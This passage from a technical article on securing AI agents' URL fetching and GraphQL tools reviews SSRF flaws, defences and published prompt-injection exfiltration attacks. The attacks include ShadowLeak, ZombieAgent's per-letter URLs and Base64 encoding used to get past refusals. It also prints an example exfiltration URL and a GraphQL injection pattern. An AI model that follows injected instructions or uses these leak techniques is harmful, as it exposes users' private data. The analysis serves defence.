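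        if not reply.is_redirect:
            return reply
        url = urljoin(url, reply.headers["Location"])
    raise Refused("too many redirects")
```

The first function splits the URL into its parts and compares the scheme, host and port with the permitted values. It also looks up the server's IP address and rejects the address if it isn't public. The second function connects to the address that passed the check and repeats the whole procedure for every redirect. Published flaws in LangChain's packages show why each step is necessary.

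#### Comparing whole hosts instead of prefixes

Testing whether the URL begins with `https://api.shop.example` is not a safe substitute for parsing it, as CVE-2026-26019 shows. The flaw, described in GitHub's advisory, was in RecursiveUrlLoader, a crawler that follows links between web pages. Its URLs came from those links, not from a model, but host code that checks model-written URLs can contain the same mistake.

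By default, the crawler was supposed to stay on the site where it started. But it accepted any link that began with the starting address, so a crawl of `https://example.com` could continue to `https://example.com.attacker.com`. The end of a domain name determines who controls it, so the second address belongs to whoever owns attacker.com. That person could run a server there or point the name at a machine inside the crawler's network.

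LangChain's Python crawler had a similar flaw two years earlier. GitLab's *CVE-2024-0243* (2024) gives an example in which the crawler starts at `https://example.com` and moves on to `https://example.completely.different`. The second address begins with the whole of the first, which suggests that this crawler also compared prefixes.

An address such as `https://api.shop.example@attacker.example` would also pass a prefix test, but the request would go to attacker.example, because everything between the two slashes and the @ sign is a user name. Ending the permitted prefix with a slash would block all these addresses, but the check would then depend on a character that is easy to forget. APIChain parses the URL, so the slash makes no difference there. The contributor who repaired the four tools included the slash only for style.

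LangChain fixed the crawler in version 1.1.14 by comparing the scheme, host and port together. OSV's *CVE-2026-26019* (2026) gives the flaw a severity of 4.1, well below the 7.5 for APIChain's. The score is lower partly because an attacker had to get a link onto a crawled page and wait for somebody to run the crawler. It is also based on only a small loss of confidentiality, which seems too small for a flaw that could expose cloud credentials.

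#### Refusing private addresses

Anybody who owns a domain can make it point to an internal address such as 10.0.0.5. Checking only the name won't catch this, so the host code also has to look up the domain's numerical addresses and refuse any that aren't public. GovTech, the Singapore government's technology agency, offers a Python library that does this for ordinary web requests.

The code above tests whether an address is global, which in Python is safer than testing whether it is private. GitHub's advisory lists 100.100.100.200 as another metadata address. It belongs to a shared range that Python classifies as neither private nor global, so a check that blocks only private addresses would let it through.

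This step adds little protection if the tool can contact only the shop, because an attacker would first have to tamper with the shop's domain records. It is essential for a tool that may read any public website, because the developer can't list the permitted hosts in advance. If the shop's API is on a private network, the developer has to make an exception for its address, but shouldn't allow the whole range of private addresses.

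An attacker can also get past the check if the code looks up the hostname twice. GitLab's *CVE-2026-41488* (2026) describes code in `langchain-openai` that fetched images to count their tokens. The code resolved the hostname once to check it and again to fetch the image. An attacker who controlled the name could return a public address the first time and a private one the second time, a technique called DNS rebinding. In the outline above, `fetch` connects directly to the address that `check_url` approved, so there is no second lookup.

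This flaw had a severity score of only 3.1 because the code used the response just to measure the image and never returned it. The attacker could at most infer from delays and errors whether an internal service existed. Such a mistake would be worse in APIChain, because it passes the text of the response to the model to use in its answer.

#### Checking every redirect

A server can answer a request with a redirect, which tells the caller to fetch another address. The repaired crawler in version 1.1.14 checked the first URL but then let its HTTP function follow redirects automatically, so a link to a harmless-looking public site could still lead to the metadata service. OSV's *GHSA-mphv-75cg-56wg* (2026), which describes this flaw, appeared two weeks after the advisory for the original one. LangChain's second repair, in version 1.1.18, turned off automatic redirects, checked each new address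 before following it and limited the number of redirects.

APIChain appears to have a similar gap. Its domain check runs once, before the request, and Python's `requests` library follows redirects unless the developer turns them off. To exploit this, an attacker needs a page on the permitted host that redirects elsewhere. Many login pages do this by sending the visitor to an address given in their query string.

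#### Restricting the network as well

All these checks depend on the host code and the HTTP library interpreting a URL the same way, which they may not do for unusual input, such as a backslash where a slash belongs. Network restrictions limit the damage if a bad URL gets through. LangChain recommends using its request tools with a proxy server, a separate machine that forwards requests and can refuse some. GitHub advised users who couldn't upgrade the crawler immediately to run it where it couldn't reach metadata or internal services. If the agent's machine can open connections only to the shop's API, a parsing mistake won't give an attacker access to the rest of the company's network.

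### What a correct domain allowlist leaves open

Even a perfect allowlist determines only which server receives the request. The table compares a prefix test with an exact comparison of scheme, host and port. The customer in the conversation owns only order 1042.

| URL that the model writes | Prefix test | Exact comparison |
|---|---|---|
| `https://api.shop.example/v1/orders/1042` | allowed | allowed |
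| `https://api.shop.example.attacker.example/` | allowed | refused |
| `http://169.254.169.254/` | refused | refused |
| `https://api.shop.example/v1/orders/1024` | allowed | allowed |
| `https://api.shop.example/v1/customers/77` | allowed | allowed |

The last two requests go to the right server, but they are for a stranger's order and a customer's account. If the host code attaches the shop's shared token, the API will probably return both. With that token, the agent could also use an endpoint that lists all orders, or an undocumented administrative endpoint if the model guessed its path or found it in injected text. With the general request tools, the model can also choose the method, and a DELETE request to a permitted host passes the same domain check as a GET.

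An allowlist doesn't keep an attacker's text out either, because an attacker can write a gift message or product review that is stored on the shop's own server. The problem is worse if the list includes a site where anyone can publish, such as a code-hosting service, because an attacker can put a page of instructions there.

The developer can add rules for methods and paths. Suppose the host code accepts only GET requests whose path is `/v1/orders/` followed by four to eight digits. The model still writes a complete URL, but it can vary only the order number, as with `get_order`. This is now limited access, plus a URL parser that can go wrong. The host code still needs object-level authorization to refuse order 1024. Letting the model write URLs is useful only if the permitted paths are too varied to offer as separate tools, but the more varied they are, the harder it is to write precise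 rules for them.

NVIDIA recommends strict parameters for every call to an external service. It also says each call should have only the lowest level of privilege held by anyone whose text has entered the prompt during the interaction. This rule would be awkward in the shop, because a stranger's gift message in the context would stop the agent from looking up the customer's own order, which the stranger has no right to see.

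With `get_order`, the developer can avoid this problem by removing the gift message from the reply before the model reads it. This is much harder if the model can fetch any path, because the developer would have to know which fields in every possible API reply contain other people's text.

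## Does it help to forbid the model to compose new URLs?

An agent that may read public websites can leak private data by putting it in a URL, even if the host code refuses every internal address and never sends the shop's token to another server. OpenAI and Anthropic therefore restrict their models to URLs that already exist somewhere else. This greatly reduces how much each request can leak, but a model can still convey information by which existing URL it chooses.

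### How a request that only reads can send data out

Suppose the shop's agent can also open web pages, for example to read a courier's tracking page. A customer asks about order 1042, and the gift message on that order contains instructions for the model. The model follows them, takes the delivery address from the order and opens this URL:

```
https://attacker.example/track?to=12+Mill+Lane
```

The request is an ordinary GET and needn't change anything on the server. But the server receives the whole URL, and servers commonly log the URLs they receive. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that the attacker can then read the stolen value in those logs. This works even if the server returns a blank page. Sending private data to someone who should not have it is called exfiltration, and this form of it is URL-based exfiltration.

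A model can leak private data through a URL even without a tool for opening pages. Many chat programs display answers written in Markdown, a simple notation that can include an image by giving its URL. If the model's answer includes such an image, the user's browser requests it as soon as the answer appears. Willison (2023), a software developer, describes how injected text can make the model put encoded private data in the query string of the image's URL. A rule about URLs therefore has to cover the model's answers as well as its tool calls.

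### How often does a model leak if nothing stops it?

*Silent Egress*, by Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay (2026), measured how often this attack works on an agent with no restrictions. (Egress is network traffic that leaves a system.) The agent was built on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model. The user always asked the agent to summarise a web page, and the model's context included a secret such as an API key. An instruction on the page told the model to send the secret to a server that recorded whatever arrived.

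The researchers put the instruction in the page's title, description, body or link text. The agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and the instruction asked for the secret whole or in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%). In 95% of those cases the summary showed no sign of this, so a filter on the model's answers would have missed nearly all the leaks. In 120 other runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the server.

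These rates are for an easy target, since the researchers placed the secret directly in the context, specified the web tool's format and gave the model almost no other instructions. They suspect that larger models may be more vulnerable because they use tools and follow instructions more reliably, but they tested only this model. OpenAI, by contrast, reports that most of the attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because safety training makes the model refuse.

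#### Splitting the secret into pieces

The first request leaked sensitive data in 96.7% of runs when the instruction asked for the whole secret, and in 26.3% when it asked for the secret in four pieces. The agent still contacted the attacker's server in about 77% of the split runs, compared with 99% of the others, so this 73% relative drop doesn't mean that the attacker got 73% less data. Each request just contained less that a filter could recognise, since four characters of a key can look like harmless usage data.

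The 26.3% is also hard to interpret. The paper defines a leak as a run in which any fragment of the secret appears in the first request. Checking the first three requests should therefore find at least as many leaks, but the reported figure is lower, at 15.8%, so the scoring can't have followed the definition. The paper also defines a completion rate, the share of runs in which all the pieces arrive, but doesn't report it.

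#### Warnings in the prompt and checks on the request

Lan and colleagues then tested defences, using the version of the attack with the instruction in the page's body and the secret sent whole.

| Defence | Runs that leaked, out of 30 |
|---|---|
| None | 30 |
| Standing instruction to ignore commands in web content | 20 |
| Tags that mark web content as untrusted | 30 |
| Both of these | 17 |
| Domain allowlist | 0 |
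| Block on suspicious addresses and paths | 0 |
| Keyword filter on URLs | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking values in URLs | 0 |

The instruction and the tags rely on the model to change its behavior, and more than half of the attacks still succeeded with both in place. The difference between 20 and 17 runs could easily be chance. Host code enforces the allowlist whatever the model writes. No attacks succeeded with the allowlist, which was predictable because the attacker's domain was not on it.

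The zeros for the last two filters are less convincing. The model attempted a leak in only 23% of runs with the keyword filter and in none with the entropy filter, although a check on finished URLs has no obvious way of changing what the model writes. The paper suggests that the model avoids random-looking values when such monitoring is active. But the entropy filter would have let through the paper's own example of a key, because it blocks only values with an entropy (a measure of randomness) above 4 bits per character and the example has about 3.8. It also ignores values of ten characters or fewer, so a key split into four-character pieces would pass.

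The study didn't test a ban on composing URLs, but one would have stopped these attacks, which all required the model to insert the secret into a URL. OpenAI adopted such a ban for ChatGPT after researchers found ways around weaker rules.

### How ChatGPT's rules changed

#### The image check of December 2023

Johann Rehberger, an independent security researcher, reported the image leak to OpenAI in April 2023. Microsoft fixed the same flaw in Bing Chat that May by generally preventing images from loading. OpenAI released its first fix in December.

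Rehberger examined ChatGPT's check on image URLs in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. Before displaying an image, the ChatGPT website sent its address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe`, which classified it as safe or unsafe. OpenAI didn't disclose the criteria. Rehberger tried 36 image addresses on his own server, one for each letter and digit, and nine passed. That was enough to send the word "hi" to his server with one request per letter. He couldn't tell why the address for "a" passed and the one for "d" didn't.

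OpenAI had built the check into the website, so the iPhone app didn't have it. Rehberger suggested limiting the number of images in each answer. Willison called OpenAI's fix half-baked and expected attackers to hide data in file names or subdomains.

The security company Tenable (2025) later got past `url_safe` as well. One of its methods used Bing redirect links to leak data one character at a time, according to eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Bugs Put Private Data at Risk*.

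#### ShadowLeak

The `url_safe` check applied to images and links in the conversation. ChatGPT's Deep Research mode, which browses the web and can read a user's Gmail, opens pages with its own tool. The security company Radware found no comparable limit on the addresses that tool could open.

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an attack that starts with an email about a company restructuring. The email contains instructions for the agent, which the sender can hide from the victim with white text or tiny fonts. When the victim asks Deep Research to study their inbox, the agent reads the email, finds an employee's name and home address in another message, adds them to a URL on the attacker's server and opens it. The request comes from OpenAI's computers, so the victim's employer can't see it on its own network.

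Radware's early attempts failed. The agent refused direct instructions to send personal data, and it searched the web for suspicious URLs instead of opening them. Later attempts got it to open the URL, but sometimes without the data. The attack worked when Radware told the model to first convert the data to Base64, a standard way of writing any data with 64 characters, and presented this as a security measure. According to Radware, this worked because the software carrying out the request then received only a harmless-looking string.

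Radware claims a 100% success rate in repeated tests. OpenAI's 50% figure for an email about staff changes appears to refer to the same attack, since the email OpenAI quotes matches the one Radware published. Radware had several working variants, which may account for some of the difference. Radware reported the flaw in June 2025 and says OpenAI had fixed it by early August. In The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*, a Radware spokesperson said the company had not seen anyone exploit the flaw.

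#### ZombieAgent and the list of prepared addresses

According to Radware, OpenAI responded to attacks of this type by forbidding ChatGPT to modify URLs. ChatGPT would open a URL only exactly as provided and refused to add parameters, even when instructed to.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* presents a way around this rule. Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* dates the report to 8 January 2026. The attacker sends an email containing 37 complete URLs, one for each letter, one for each digit and one for a space, with instructions to spell out the private data by opening the URLs in turn. ChatGPT opens each URL exactly as given, and the attacker reads the text from the order of the requests. In case the order gets lost, Radware also prepared a separate set of URLs for each position in the text, so that each request shows both a character and its position.

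The leak could also continue after the conversation ended. OpenAI had stopped ChatGPT from opening an attacker's addresses stored in its memory, the notes it keeps between conversations. Radware instead planted a rule in the memory that made ChatGPT reread the attacker's email, which contained the addresses, whenever the user sent a message. Radware reported the flaws on 26 September 2025 and says OpenAI fixed them on 16 December.

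#### Only addresses that a web index has seen

OpenAI described a stricter rule on 28 January 2026. ChatGPT may load a URL automatically only if OpenAI's crawler has already recorded that exact URL. The crawler records public web pages and has no access to users' conversations. If the URL has not been recorded, the agent has to try another website, or the user gets a warning that the link may include information from the conversation.

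A URL that contains one customer's street address is very unlikely to be in the index, so the attack in the shop example fails. OpenAI preferred this check to a list of trusted websites, partly because trusted sites can redirect elsewhere and partly because people learn to click through frequent warnings. OpenAI uses the same check for navigation in its Atlas browser and for searches and navigation in Deep Research.

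Rehberger considers the rule a significant improvement but not a complete solution. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he points out that an attacker can still leak data by using a separate URL for each letter, if all the URLs are in the index. OpenAI's paper on the rule acknowledges this weakness. The owner of a large blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, enough for every letter and digit. An attacker could also use thousands of pages and give the model a table of what each one stands for. Under the earlier rule, the attacker could make up the addresses while writing the email. Now the pages have to be public first, which takes some preparation but no special access.

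He also doubts that every developer at OpenAI will know about the check and use it in new features. The Mac and iPhone apps had lacked the earlier check.

### Anthropic's web fetch tool

Anthropic's web fetch tool for its Claude models checks URLs against the conversation instead of an index. In the version that Anthropic documented in early 2026, the tool could open a URL only if it had already appeared in a user's message, in the result of a tool run by the developer's own code, or in an earlier search or fetch result. It rejected URLs that the model made up and URLs produced by code running in Anthropic's sandbox.

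URLs could be at most 250 characters long. Developers could limit the number of fetches with `max_uses` and restrict the tool to particular sites with `allowed_domains`. By default, the number of fetches was unlimited. Anthropic acknowledged a "residual risk" and advised developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive.

Willison (2025) approved of the ban on made-up URLs but objected to allowing URLs from the user's message, where developers often paste untrusted text, and from tool results, which can also contain it. In the shop, if the reply from `get_order` includes the gift message, the model is allowed to open every link in that message. Whoever wrote it could supply a full set of prepared addresses, as Radware did by email. A developer who builds a similar rule could avoid this by accepting only URLs that the customer typed.

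Links from earlier fetch results can also be used to extract private data. Willison (2026) reports how Ayush Paul tricked the Claude chat app, which remembers facts about its user from past conversations. Paul set up a website that posed as a login check for AI assistants and asked Claude to find the user's profile by going through the site letter by letter. The rule permitted every request because each link appeared on the page Claude had just fetched. By following the links, Claude revealed the user's name, home city and employer to the site. The site served these pages only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, which made the trick harder for others to notice.

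Anthropic said it had already identified the flaw internally. It has since stopped the tool from following links in pages it has fetched, which also prevents legitimate browsing from page to page.

The `allowed_domains` setting is a stronger restriction, but a permitted site can still pass data to an attacker. Superhuman, an email program, allowed images from docs.google.com, where an attacker's Google Form can store data sent in a GET request. Willison describes how text injected into one email leaked the contents of dozens of others this way.

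### How much can a choice among fixed addresses leak?

Suppose the agent makes $k$ requests, each to one of $n$ permitted addresses, and the attacker can see all of them in order. There are $n$ possibilities for each request and so $n^k$ possible sequences. A bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question, and picking out one of $M$ possibilities takes $\log_2 M$ bits. The sequence can therefore carry at most

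$$\log_2(n^k) = k \log_2 n \text{ bits}$$

With Radware's 37 addresses, each request carries $\log_2 37$, or about 5.2 bits. Eight characters drawn from the same 37 symbols contain about 41.7 bits, so sending them takes eight requests. With 4,096 addresses, each request carries 12 bits, and four requests are enough. If the model can compose the URL, it can include 200 characters from a 64-symbol alphabet such as Base64, at 6 bits each, and send 1,200 bits in a single request.

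| What the model may open | Bits per request | Requests for 8 characters | Requests for 1,200 bits |
|---|---|---|---|
| 37 fixed addresses | 5.2 | 8 | 231 |
| 4,096 fixed addresses | 12 | 4 | 100 |
| Any URL with 200 free characters | 1,200 | 1 | 1 |

Restricting the model to fixed addresses cuts the rate of leakage by a factor of 100 or more in these examples, but doesn't stop it. Whether that is good enough depends on the secret. Copying out a customer's whole order history would take thousands of requests, which somebody would probably notice. A six-digit login code is about 20 bits, so it can leak in four requests if the model has 37 addresses to choose from, or two if it has 4,096.

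An agent can leak information even if it can open only one address. An attacker could ask the model to open that address only if the customer has a refund pending, and see whether a request arrives. The formula gives zero bits here because it assumes a fixed number of requests. If the agent can make anywhere from zero to $k$ requests, we can count "no request" as an extra address, and the bound becomes $k \log_2(n+1)$. Neither bound includes what an attacker might learn from when the requests arrive.

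Doubling the number of requests doubles the total amount of data a model can leak, whereas doubling the number of addresses adds only one bit per request. If `max_uses` limits the model to five fetches and it has 4,096 addresses to choose from, it can leak at most 60 bits, or about 11 characters. However, the limit applies separately to each call to Anthropic's API, so the total grows over a long conversation. Radware exploited the same weakness with a planted memory, which gave the attacker new requests in every later conversation.

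A limit on URL length gives little protection by itself. The 200 free characters in the example would fit into a 250-character URL, so most of the protection in Anthropic's design comes from the ban on composing URLs.

### Caching and repeat visits

Rehberger proposes two additions to OpenAI's rule. The agent's software could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it if the model requests the page again, so that the attacker's server receives only one request. Alternatively, the software could refuse to open the same URL twice in a session. He expects some data to leak with either measure.

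With one address per character, the attacker could no longer receive "1001", because the model would have to open the addresses for 0 and 1 twice each. If the model could use each of 37 addresses only once, its requests could also carry at most about 145 bits, equivalent to 28 characters, however long the session lasted. If the requests also arrived in an unpredictable order, the attacker would learn only which addresses the model opened, and the limit would fall to 37 bits.

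Radware already gets around both limits by using separate addresses for each position. Eight characters need 8 × 37 = 296 addresses. The model never has to open the same address twice, and the order in which the requests arrive doesn't matter. Under OpenAI's rule, the crawler would have to find all 296 pages beforehand. That is more work for the attacker, but a site with a few hundred public pages is not unusual.

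ChatGPT's optional Lockdown Mode takes caching further. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, browsing in this mode uses only cached content, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network. An attacker therefore can't observe any requests from browsing, whatever addresses the model chooses. Willison (2026) reported in June that the setting was reaching personal accounts, including free ones. Users who turn it on lose agent mode and Deep Research, according to The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*. OpenAI doesn't guarantee that data can't get out, because connected apps remain a possible route.

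## What changes when the model writes GraphQL operations?

A tool for model-written GraphQL sends every request to one fixed address. Injected text therefore can't redirect the shop's token to another server, or make this tool send a delivery address to an attacker's site, unless the API has a field that takes a URL and fetches it. But the model still chooses which of the shop's data to request. Because the records are connected, a single operation can start at the customer's own order and end at other people's details.

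### From one order to the rest of the shop

A GraphQL schema lists the API's types, the fields of each type and the kind of value each field returns. Part of the shop's schema might look like this, with an exclamation mark on values the caller must supply:

```
type Query    { me: Customer   order(id: ID!): Order }
type Order    { status: String   carrier: String   giftMessage: String
                customer: Customer   items(first: Int): [Item] }
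type Customer { name: String   email: String   orders(first: Int): [Order] }
type Item     { quantity: Int   product: Product }
type Product  { name: String   purchasePrice: Int   reviews(first: Int): [Review] }
type Review   { text: String   author: Customer }
```

Every query starts at a field of `Query` and can follow any field that returns another object, such as from an order to its customer and then to that customer's orders. A caller can discover the available types and fields through introspection, which means querying a GraphQL API for its own schema.

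The schema restricts what the model can request. *GraphQL Query Generation* (Kesarwani, Ghosh et al., 2024) gives an example in which a caller can ask for students below a certain weight but not above it, because the schema defines no such filter. But a shop usually designs its schema for its website, apps and staff, so the schema offers far more than a delivery-tracking agent needs.

If the developer writes the order query in advance, it looks like this:

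```
query GetOrderStatus($id: ID!) {
  order(id: $id) { status carrier }
}
```

The model supplies only the variable, `{"id": "1042"}`, and can't add a field by changing its value. The operation also leaves out `giftMessage`, so text a stranger wrote there never reaches the model through this tool.

A model that composes the query itself might write:

```
query {
  order(id: "1042") {
    status carrier giftMessage
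    customer { email orders(first: 100) { status giftMessage } }
  }
}
```

It could do this without any attack, simply because the extra information looked useful. The reply would contain up to 101 gift messages, any of which could hold a prompt injection.

### Apollo MCP Server's three patterns

Apollo MCP Server is an open-source program that turns GraphQL operations into MCP tools. Its maker, Apollo GraphQL, sells software for running GraphQL APIs. In *Connect AI Agents to Your GraphQL API Using MCP*, written for the company, Lawrence describes three patterns and recommends starting with operations stored in files.

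#### Operations from files

The developer puts each operation in its own file, and the server turns it into one tool. Apollo GraphQL's *Define MCP Tools* explains that the server derives the tool schema from the operation's variables and stores the operation's text separately. When the model calls the tool, the server sends the stored text unchanged. The server doesn't enforce the tool schema, so the GraphQL API has to reject values of the wrong type.

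Lawrence's example operation begins `GetUserOrders($userId: ID!, $limit: Int = 10)`. In the shop, this would let the model choose whose orders to request, so the API would have to compare the user ID with the caller's token. The limit of 10 is only a default, so the model can request 10,000 orders or send an explicit null, which GraphQL passes on instead of applying the default. Declaring the variable as `Int!` rules out the null, but to keep the limit at 10, the developer has to write the number into the operation itself.

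#### Persisted queries with a safelist

Persisted queries are operations that a developer registers in advance, here with Apollo's GraphOS platform. The MCP server turns each one into a tool. Apollo Router, the gateway in front of the API, accepts only operations on the list of registered queries, which Apollo calls a safelist.

Operation files restrict what the model can send through the MCP server, but the API might still run any query from someone who obtained the token by another route. A safelist on the API side refuses any query that isn't on the list. Chu (2025), in *Apollo MCP Server 1.0 is Generally Available*, recommends persisted queries to block malicious and resource-intensive operations in production.

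Lawrence suggests this pattern for companies that want an agent to keep pace with their existing apps. Developers should still check each operation, because a query written for an account page may fetch an address and phone number that a tracking agent doesn't need.

#### Exploration at runtime

For developers who can't predict which operations an agent will need, the server has four tools:

- `introspect` describes a type and, to a chosen depth, the types it leads to.
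- `search` finds types and fields that match search terms, along with the parent types needed to reach them.
- `validate` checks an operation against the schema without running it.
- `execute` sends an operation that the model has written.

To find order 1042, the model might search for "order" and "status", learn that `Query.order` returns an `Order`, then write and execute the query. Cloudflare's server for model-written code has similar search and execute tools.

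The model can skip `validate`, and Apollo's documents disagree about whether the server still checks the operation against the schema. Lawrence (2026), in *Where Apollo MCP Server Stands on the OWASP MCP Top 10*, writes that it does so before `execute` runs the operation. *Define MCP Tools* says that `execute` checks only the syntax and the type of operation. The difference matters little for safety, because the GraphQL API validates every request before fetching data, according to Apollo GraphQL's *Apollo MCP Server* overview.

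All four tools are off by default. Apollo GraphQL's training course *Exercise 3* advises turning off `execute` to stop the model from running arbitrary queries. *mcp-graphql*, a smaller server with one tool for reading the schema and one for running queries, describes itself as very generic and suggests that developers with specific needs write their own server that accepts only certain fields or variables.

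### Free reads with predefined writes

Apollo's server has a separate setting for mutations, the operations that change data.

| Mutation mode | Mutations the developer wrote | Mutations the model writes |
|---|---|---|
| `none` (default) | blocked | blocked |
| `explicit` | allowed | blocked |
| `all` | allowed | allowed |

Lawrence describes a common combination of free reads and predefined writes. In outline, the configuration is:

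```
operations:
  source: local
  paths: [./mutations/*.graphql]
introspection:
  execute: { enabled: true }
  search:  { enabled: true }
overrides:
  mutation_mode: explicit
```

With this setup, the shop's agent could write any query, but could request a refund only through an operation such as `RequestRefund($orderId: ID!, $reason: String!)`. This division makes sense because customers' questions vary more than the actions a shop wants to permit. However, it doesn't stop the agent from disclosing data, and the shop can't take back an address once the agent has revealed it.

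Predefined writes can also be misused. Injected text can cause the model to call `RequestRefund` with valid values. Lawrence (2026) assesses the server against an OWASP list of MCP risks and says that a fixed set of operations limits the damage from such an attack but doesn't prevent it. Once the developer has approved a mutation by adding its file, the model can call it without anyone approving the individual calls.

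That approval also holds only while the file is unchanged. If the operations come from a GraphOS collection, the server picks up edits within about a minute, without showing anyone the changes or asking for approval. Apollo GraphQL's *Apollo MCP Server Security Audit* (2026) therefore recommends that operators list everyone who can edit the source and compare the live tool definitions with a reviewed copy after each change.

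The server can require a particular OAuth scope (a named permission in the caller's token) for each tool. If refunds and order lookups have separate tools, a developer can require a different scope for each. All model-written queries go through `execute`, so they need the same scope whether they fetch a delivery status or a list of customers.

### Why GitLab keeps its operations in files

GitLab, the code-hosting company, chose predefined operations for both reads and writes. Its *MCP GraphQL Integration* tells developers to store each operation in a `.graphql` file. An automated test checks every file against the schema whenever the code changes, so GitLab finds out about a renamed field before a user does. Apollo's server doesn't check predefined operations against the schema before offering them as tools.

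Ordinary code processes the model's values before they go into the operation. For example, the model can identify an issue by its web address, and the code converts that into the internal ID the mutation needs.

GitLab considered a tool that would accept any query but rejected it, citing unauthorized queries and a lack of complexity limits among its reasons. These two objections seem overstated, because in GitLab's outline the tool would have run queries through the same schema as the predefined operations, which already checks permissions and has a default complexity limit of 200. GitLab had a stronger objection to generating tools from the whole schema, which would have exposed every mutation instead of only the approved ones. GitLab says it will consider that design again in the next iteration.

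### How a model finds its way through a large schema

A model needs the schema to write queries, but the schema may be too large to fit in its context. The GraphQL AI Working Group discussed two solutions in November 2025.

One approach uses similarity search. The agent starts at the top-level fields and uses embeddings, which are lists of numbers that represent text, to pick those closest in meaning to the user's request. It then repeats this with the types those fields lead to. According to GraphQL's recap of the group's January 2026 meeting, a small open model on a machine with 8 GB of memory produced embeddings good enough for this.

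In the other solution, people divide the schema into smaller files, called subschemas. The agent first receives one with all the accessible top-level fields and the most common types. The `@require_graphql_subschema` directive identifies which other files to load when the agent needs them. Subschemas take more work to maintain, but developers can review what the model will read.

Neither method controls access. If the API still serves `purchasePrice`, a model that has never seen the field can guess its name. Error messages make guessing easier. In Lawrence's example, a query asks for `name` on an order item, and the validator returns an error that says the field doesn't exist and suggests `productName`. Such hints help a model correct its mistakes, but they also reveal parts of the schema that the developer left out of its context.

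Obscurity doesn't protect rarely used fields either. *PrediQL* (2025) presents a testing tool in which a language model writes queries, reads the error messages and tries again. When the tool used both retrieval and error feedback, its queries covered all or nearly all of the schema for almost every API and model tested.

An Apollo contract is a version of the schema with parts actually removed for a particular audience. Chu gives the example of a support agent that can see orders but not internal profit margins. The contract restricts the agent only if the agent's requests go to an endpoint that serves just the reduced schema.

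### Valid queries that the customer may not run

Validation checks a query against the schema and catches a misspelled field, a missing argument or a number where the API requires text. Like the tool schema for `get_order`, it doesn't check whether the customer is allowed to see the data, so the queries for orders 1024 and 1042 are equally valid.

Object-level authorization on the `order` field would refuse order 1024, but a graph has more than one route to a record. This query starts from the customer's own order:

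```
query {
  order(id: "1042") {
    items(first: 1) {
      product { reviews(first: 50) { author { name email } } }
    }
  }
}
```

The query passes the ownership check, then goes from the order to a product, its reviews, and the email addresses of up to 50 strangers who wrote them. The shop's website may have displayed only the reviewers' names, so nobody noticed that `email` was available too.

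The API therefore has to check permission wherever it returns a `Customer`, and it needs a separate rule for sensitive fields such as `email`. GitLab does something similar for its fine-grained tokens. Each type and mutation needs a directive stating which permission it requires. The API denies access to any type without one, so a forgotten directive causes an error instead of a leak.

If GitLab's API denies access to an object deeper in the query, it returns null or drops the object from its list, and the tool still reports success. An agent could then tell a user that a project has three open issues when the API has omitted a fourth.

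The API also needs the caller's identity. By default, if authentication is configured, Apollo's server forwards the caller's token to the GraphQL API so the API can apply the caller's permissions. The MCP specification forbids forwarding the token because it was meant for the MCP server, not the API behind it. Turning forwarding off removes the caller's identity from the request, since the server can't yet exchange the token for a suitable one. If the developer uses a shared token instead, every model-written query runs with the shop's access. Host code would have great difficulty checking ownership in an arbitrary query, so a shared token is a much worse choice here than with `get_order`.

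### Many lookups in one request

GraphQL lets a caller give a field a temporary name, called an alias, and so request the same field several times with different arguments:

```
query {
  a: order(id: "1042") { status }
  b: order(id: "1043") { status }
  c: order(id: "1044") { status }
}
```

A rate limiter that counts HTTP requests counts a query with 500 aliased lookups as one request. If the API doesn't check who owns each order, someone could search a whole range of order numbers this way. They could also guess discount codes, or anything else that a limit on attempts is supposed to protect. The API should count the lookups in each operation as well as the requests.

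Mutations can share a request too, and GraphQL runs them one after another. GitLab's design for such requests treats the whole request as failed if any mutation fails, even if an earlier one has already taken effect. If a shop's agent sent several refunds in one request and retried it after a later one failed, it could issue the first refund twice. GitLab currently permits only one mutation per tool call.

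### Model text pasted into an operation

Host code can turn a predefined operation into a model-written one by accident. Suppose the developer builds the query by joining text:

```
"query { order(id: \"" + order_id + "\") { status carrier } }"
```

In GraphQL injection, as in SQL injection, a quotation mark in an `order_id` inserted into the operation's text can end the string early, and the rest of the value could then add fields or request another record. If the value is passed as a variable instead, the API parses the operation's text separately from the value, so the value can't alter the operation's structure.

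Variables protect only the GraphQL operation, but the API may later interpret the value as another language. For example, GitLab's comment tool puts the comment in a variable but also checks it for "quick actions". These are commands, such as closing an issue, that GitLab carries out when they appear in a comment.

Search fields have a similar problem. Shopify's `orders` field takes a `query` string with its own filter syntax. If the model writes the whole string, it decides which orders to search for, even though the GraphQL operation is predefined. A safer tool would take a date or status from the model and build the filter in host code.

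### How a cost limit refuses a query

A short query can request a huge amount of data:

```
query {
  me {
    orders(first: 100) {
      items(first: 50) { product { name } }
    }
  }
}
```

The API can estimate the size before fetching anything. It starts with the innermost object and works outwards, multiplying by the length of each list. If every object costs one point and plain values such as names cost nothing, the calculation is:

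| Object | Calculation | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| One product | 1 | 1 |
| One item with its product | 1 + 1 | 2 |
| One order with 50 items | 1 + 50 × 2 | 101 |
| The user with 100 orders | 1 + 100 × 101 | 10,101 |

The total consists of 1 user, 100 orders, 5,000 items and 5,000 products. With a limit of 1,000 objects, the API refuses the query without querying the database. The agent can then ask for fewer orders. The limit also protects the model's context, which 10,101 objects would probably fill.

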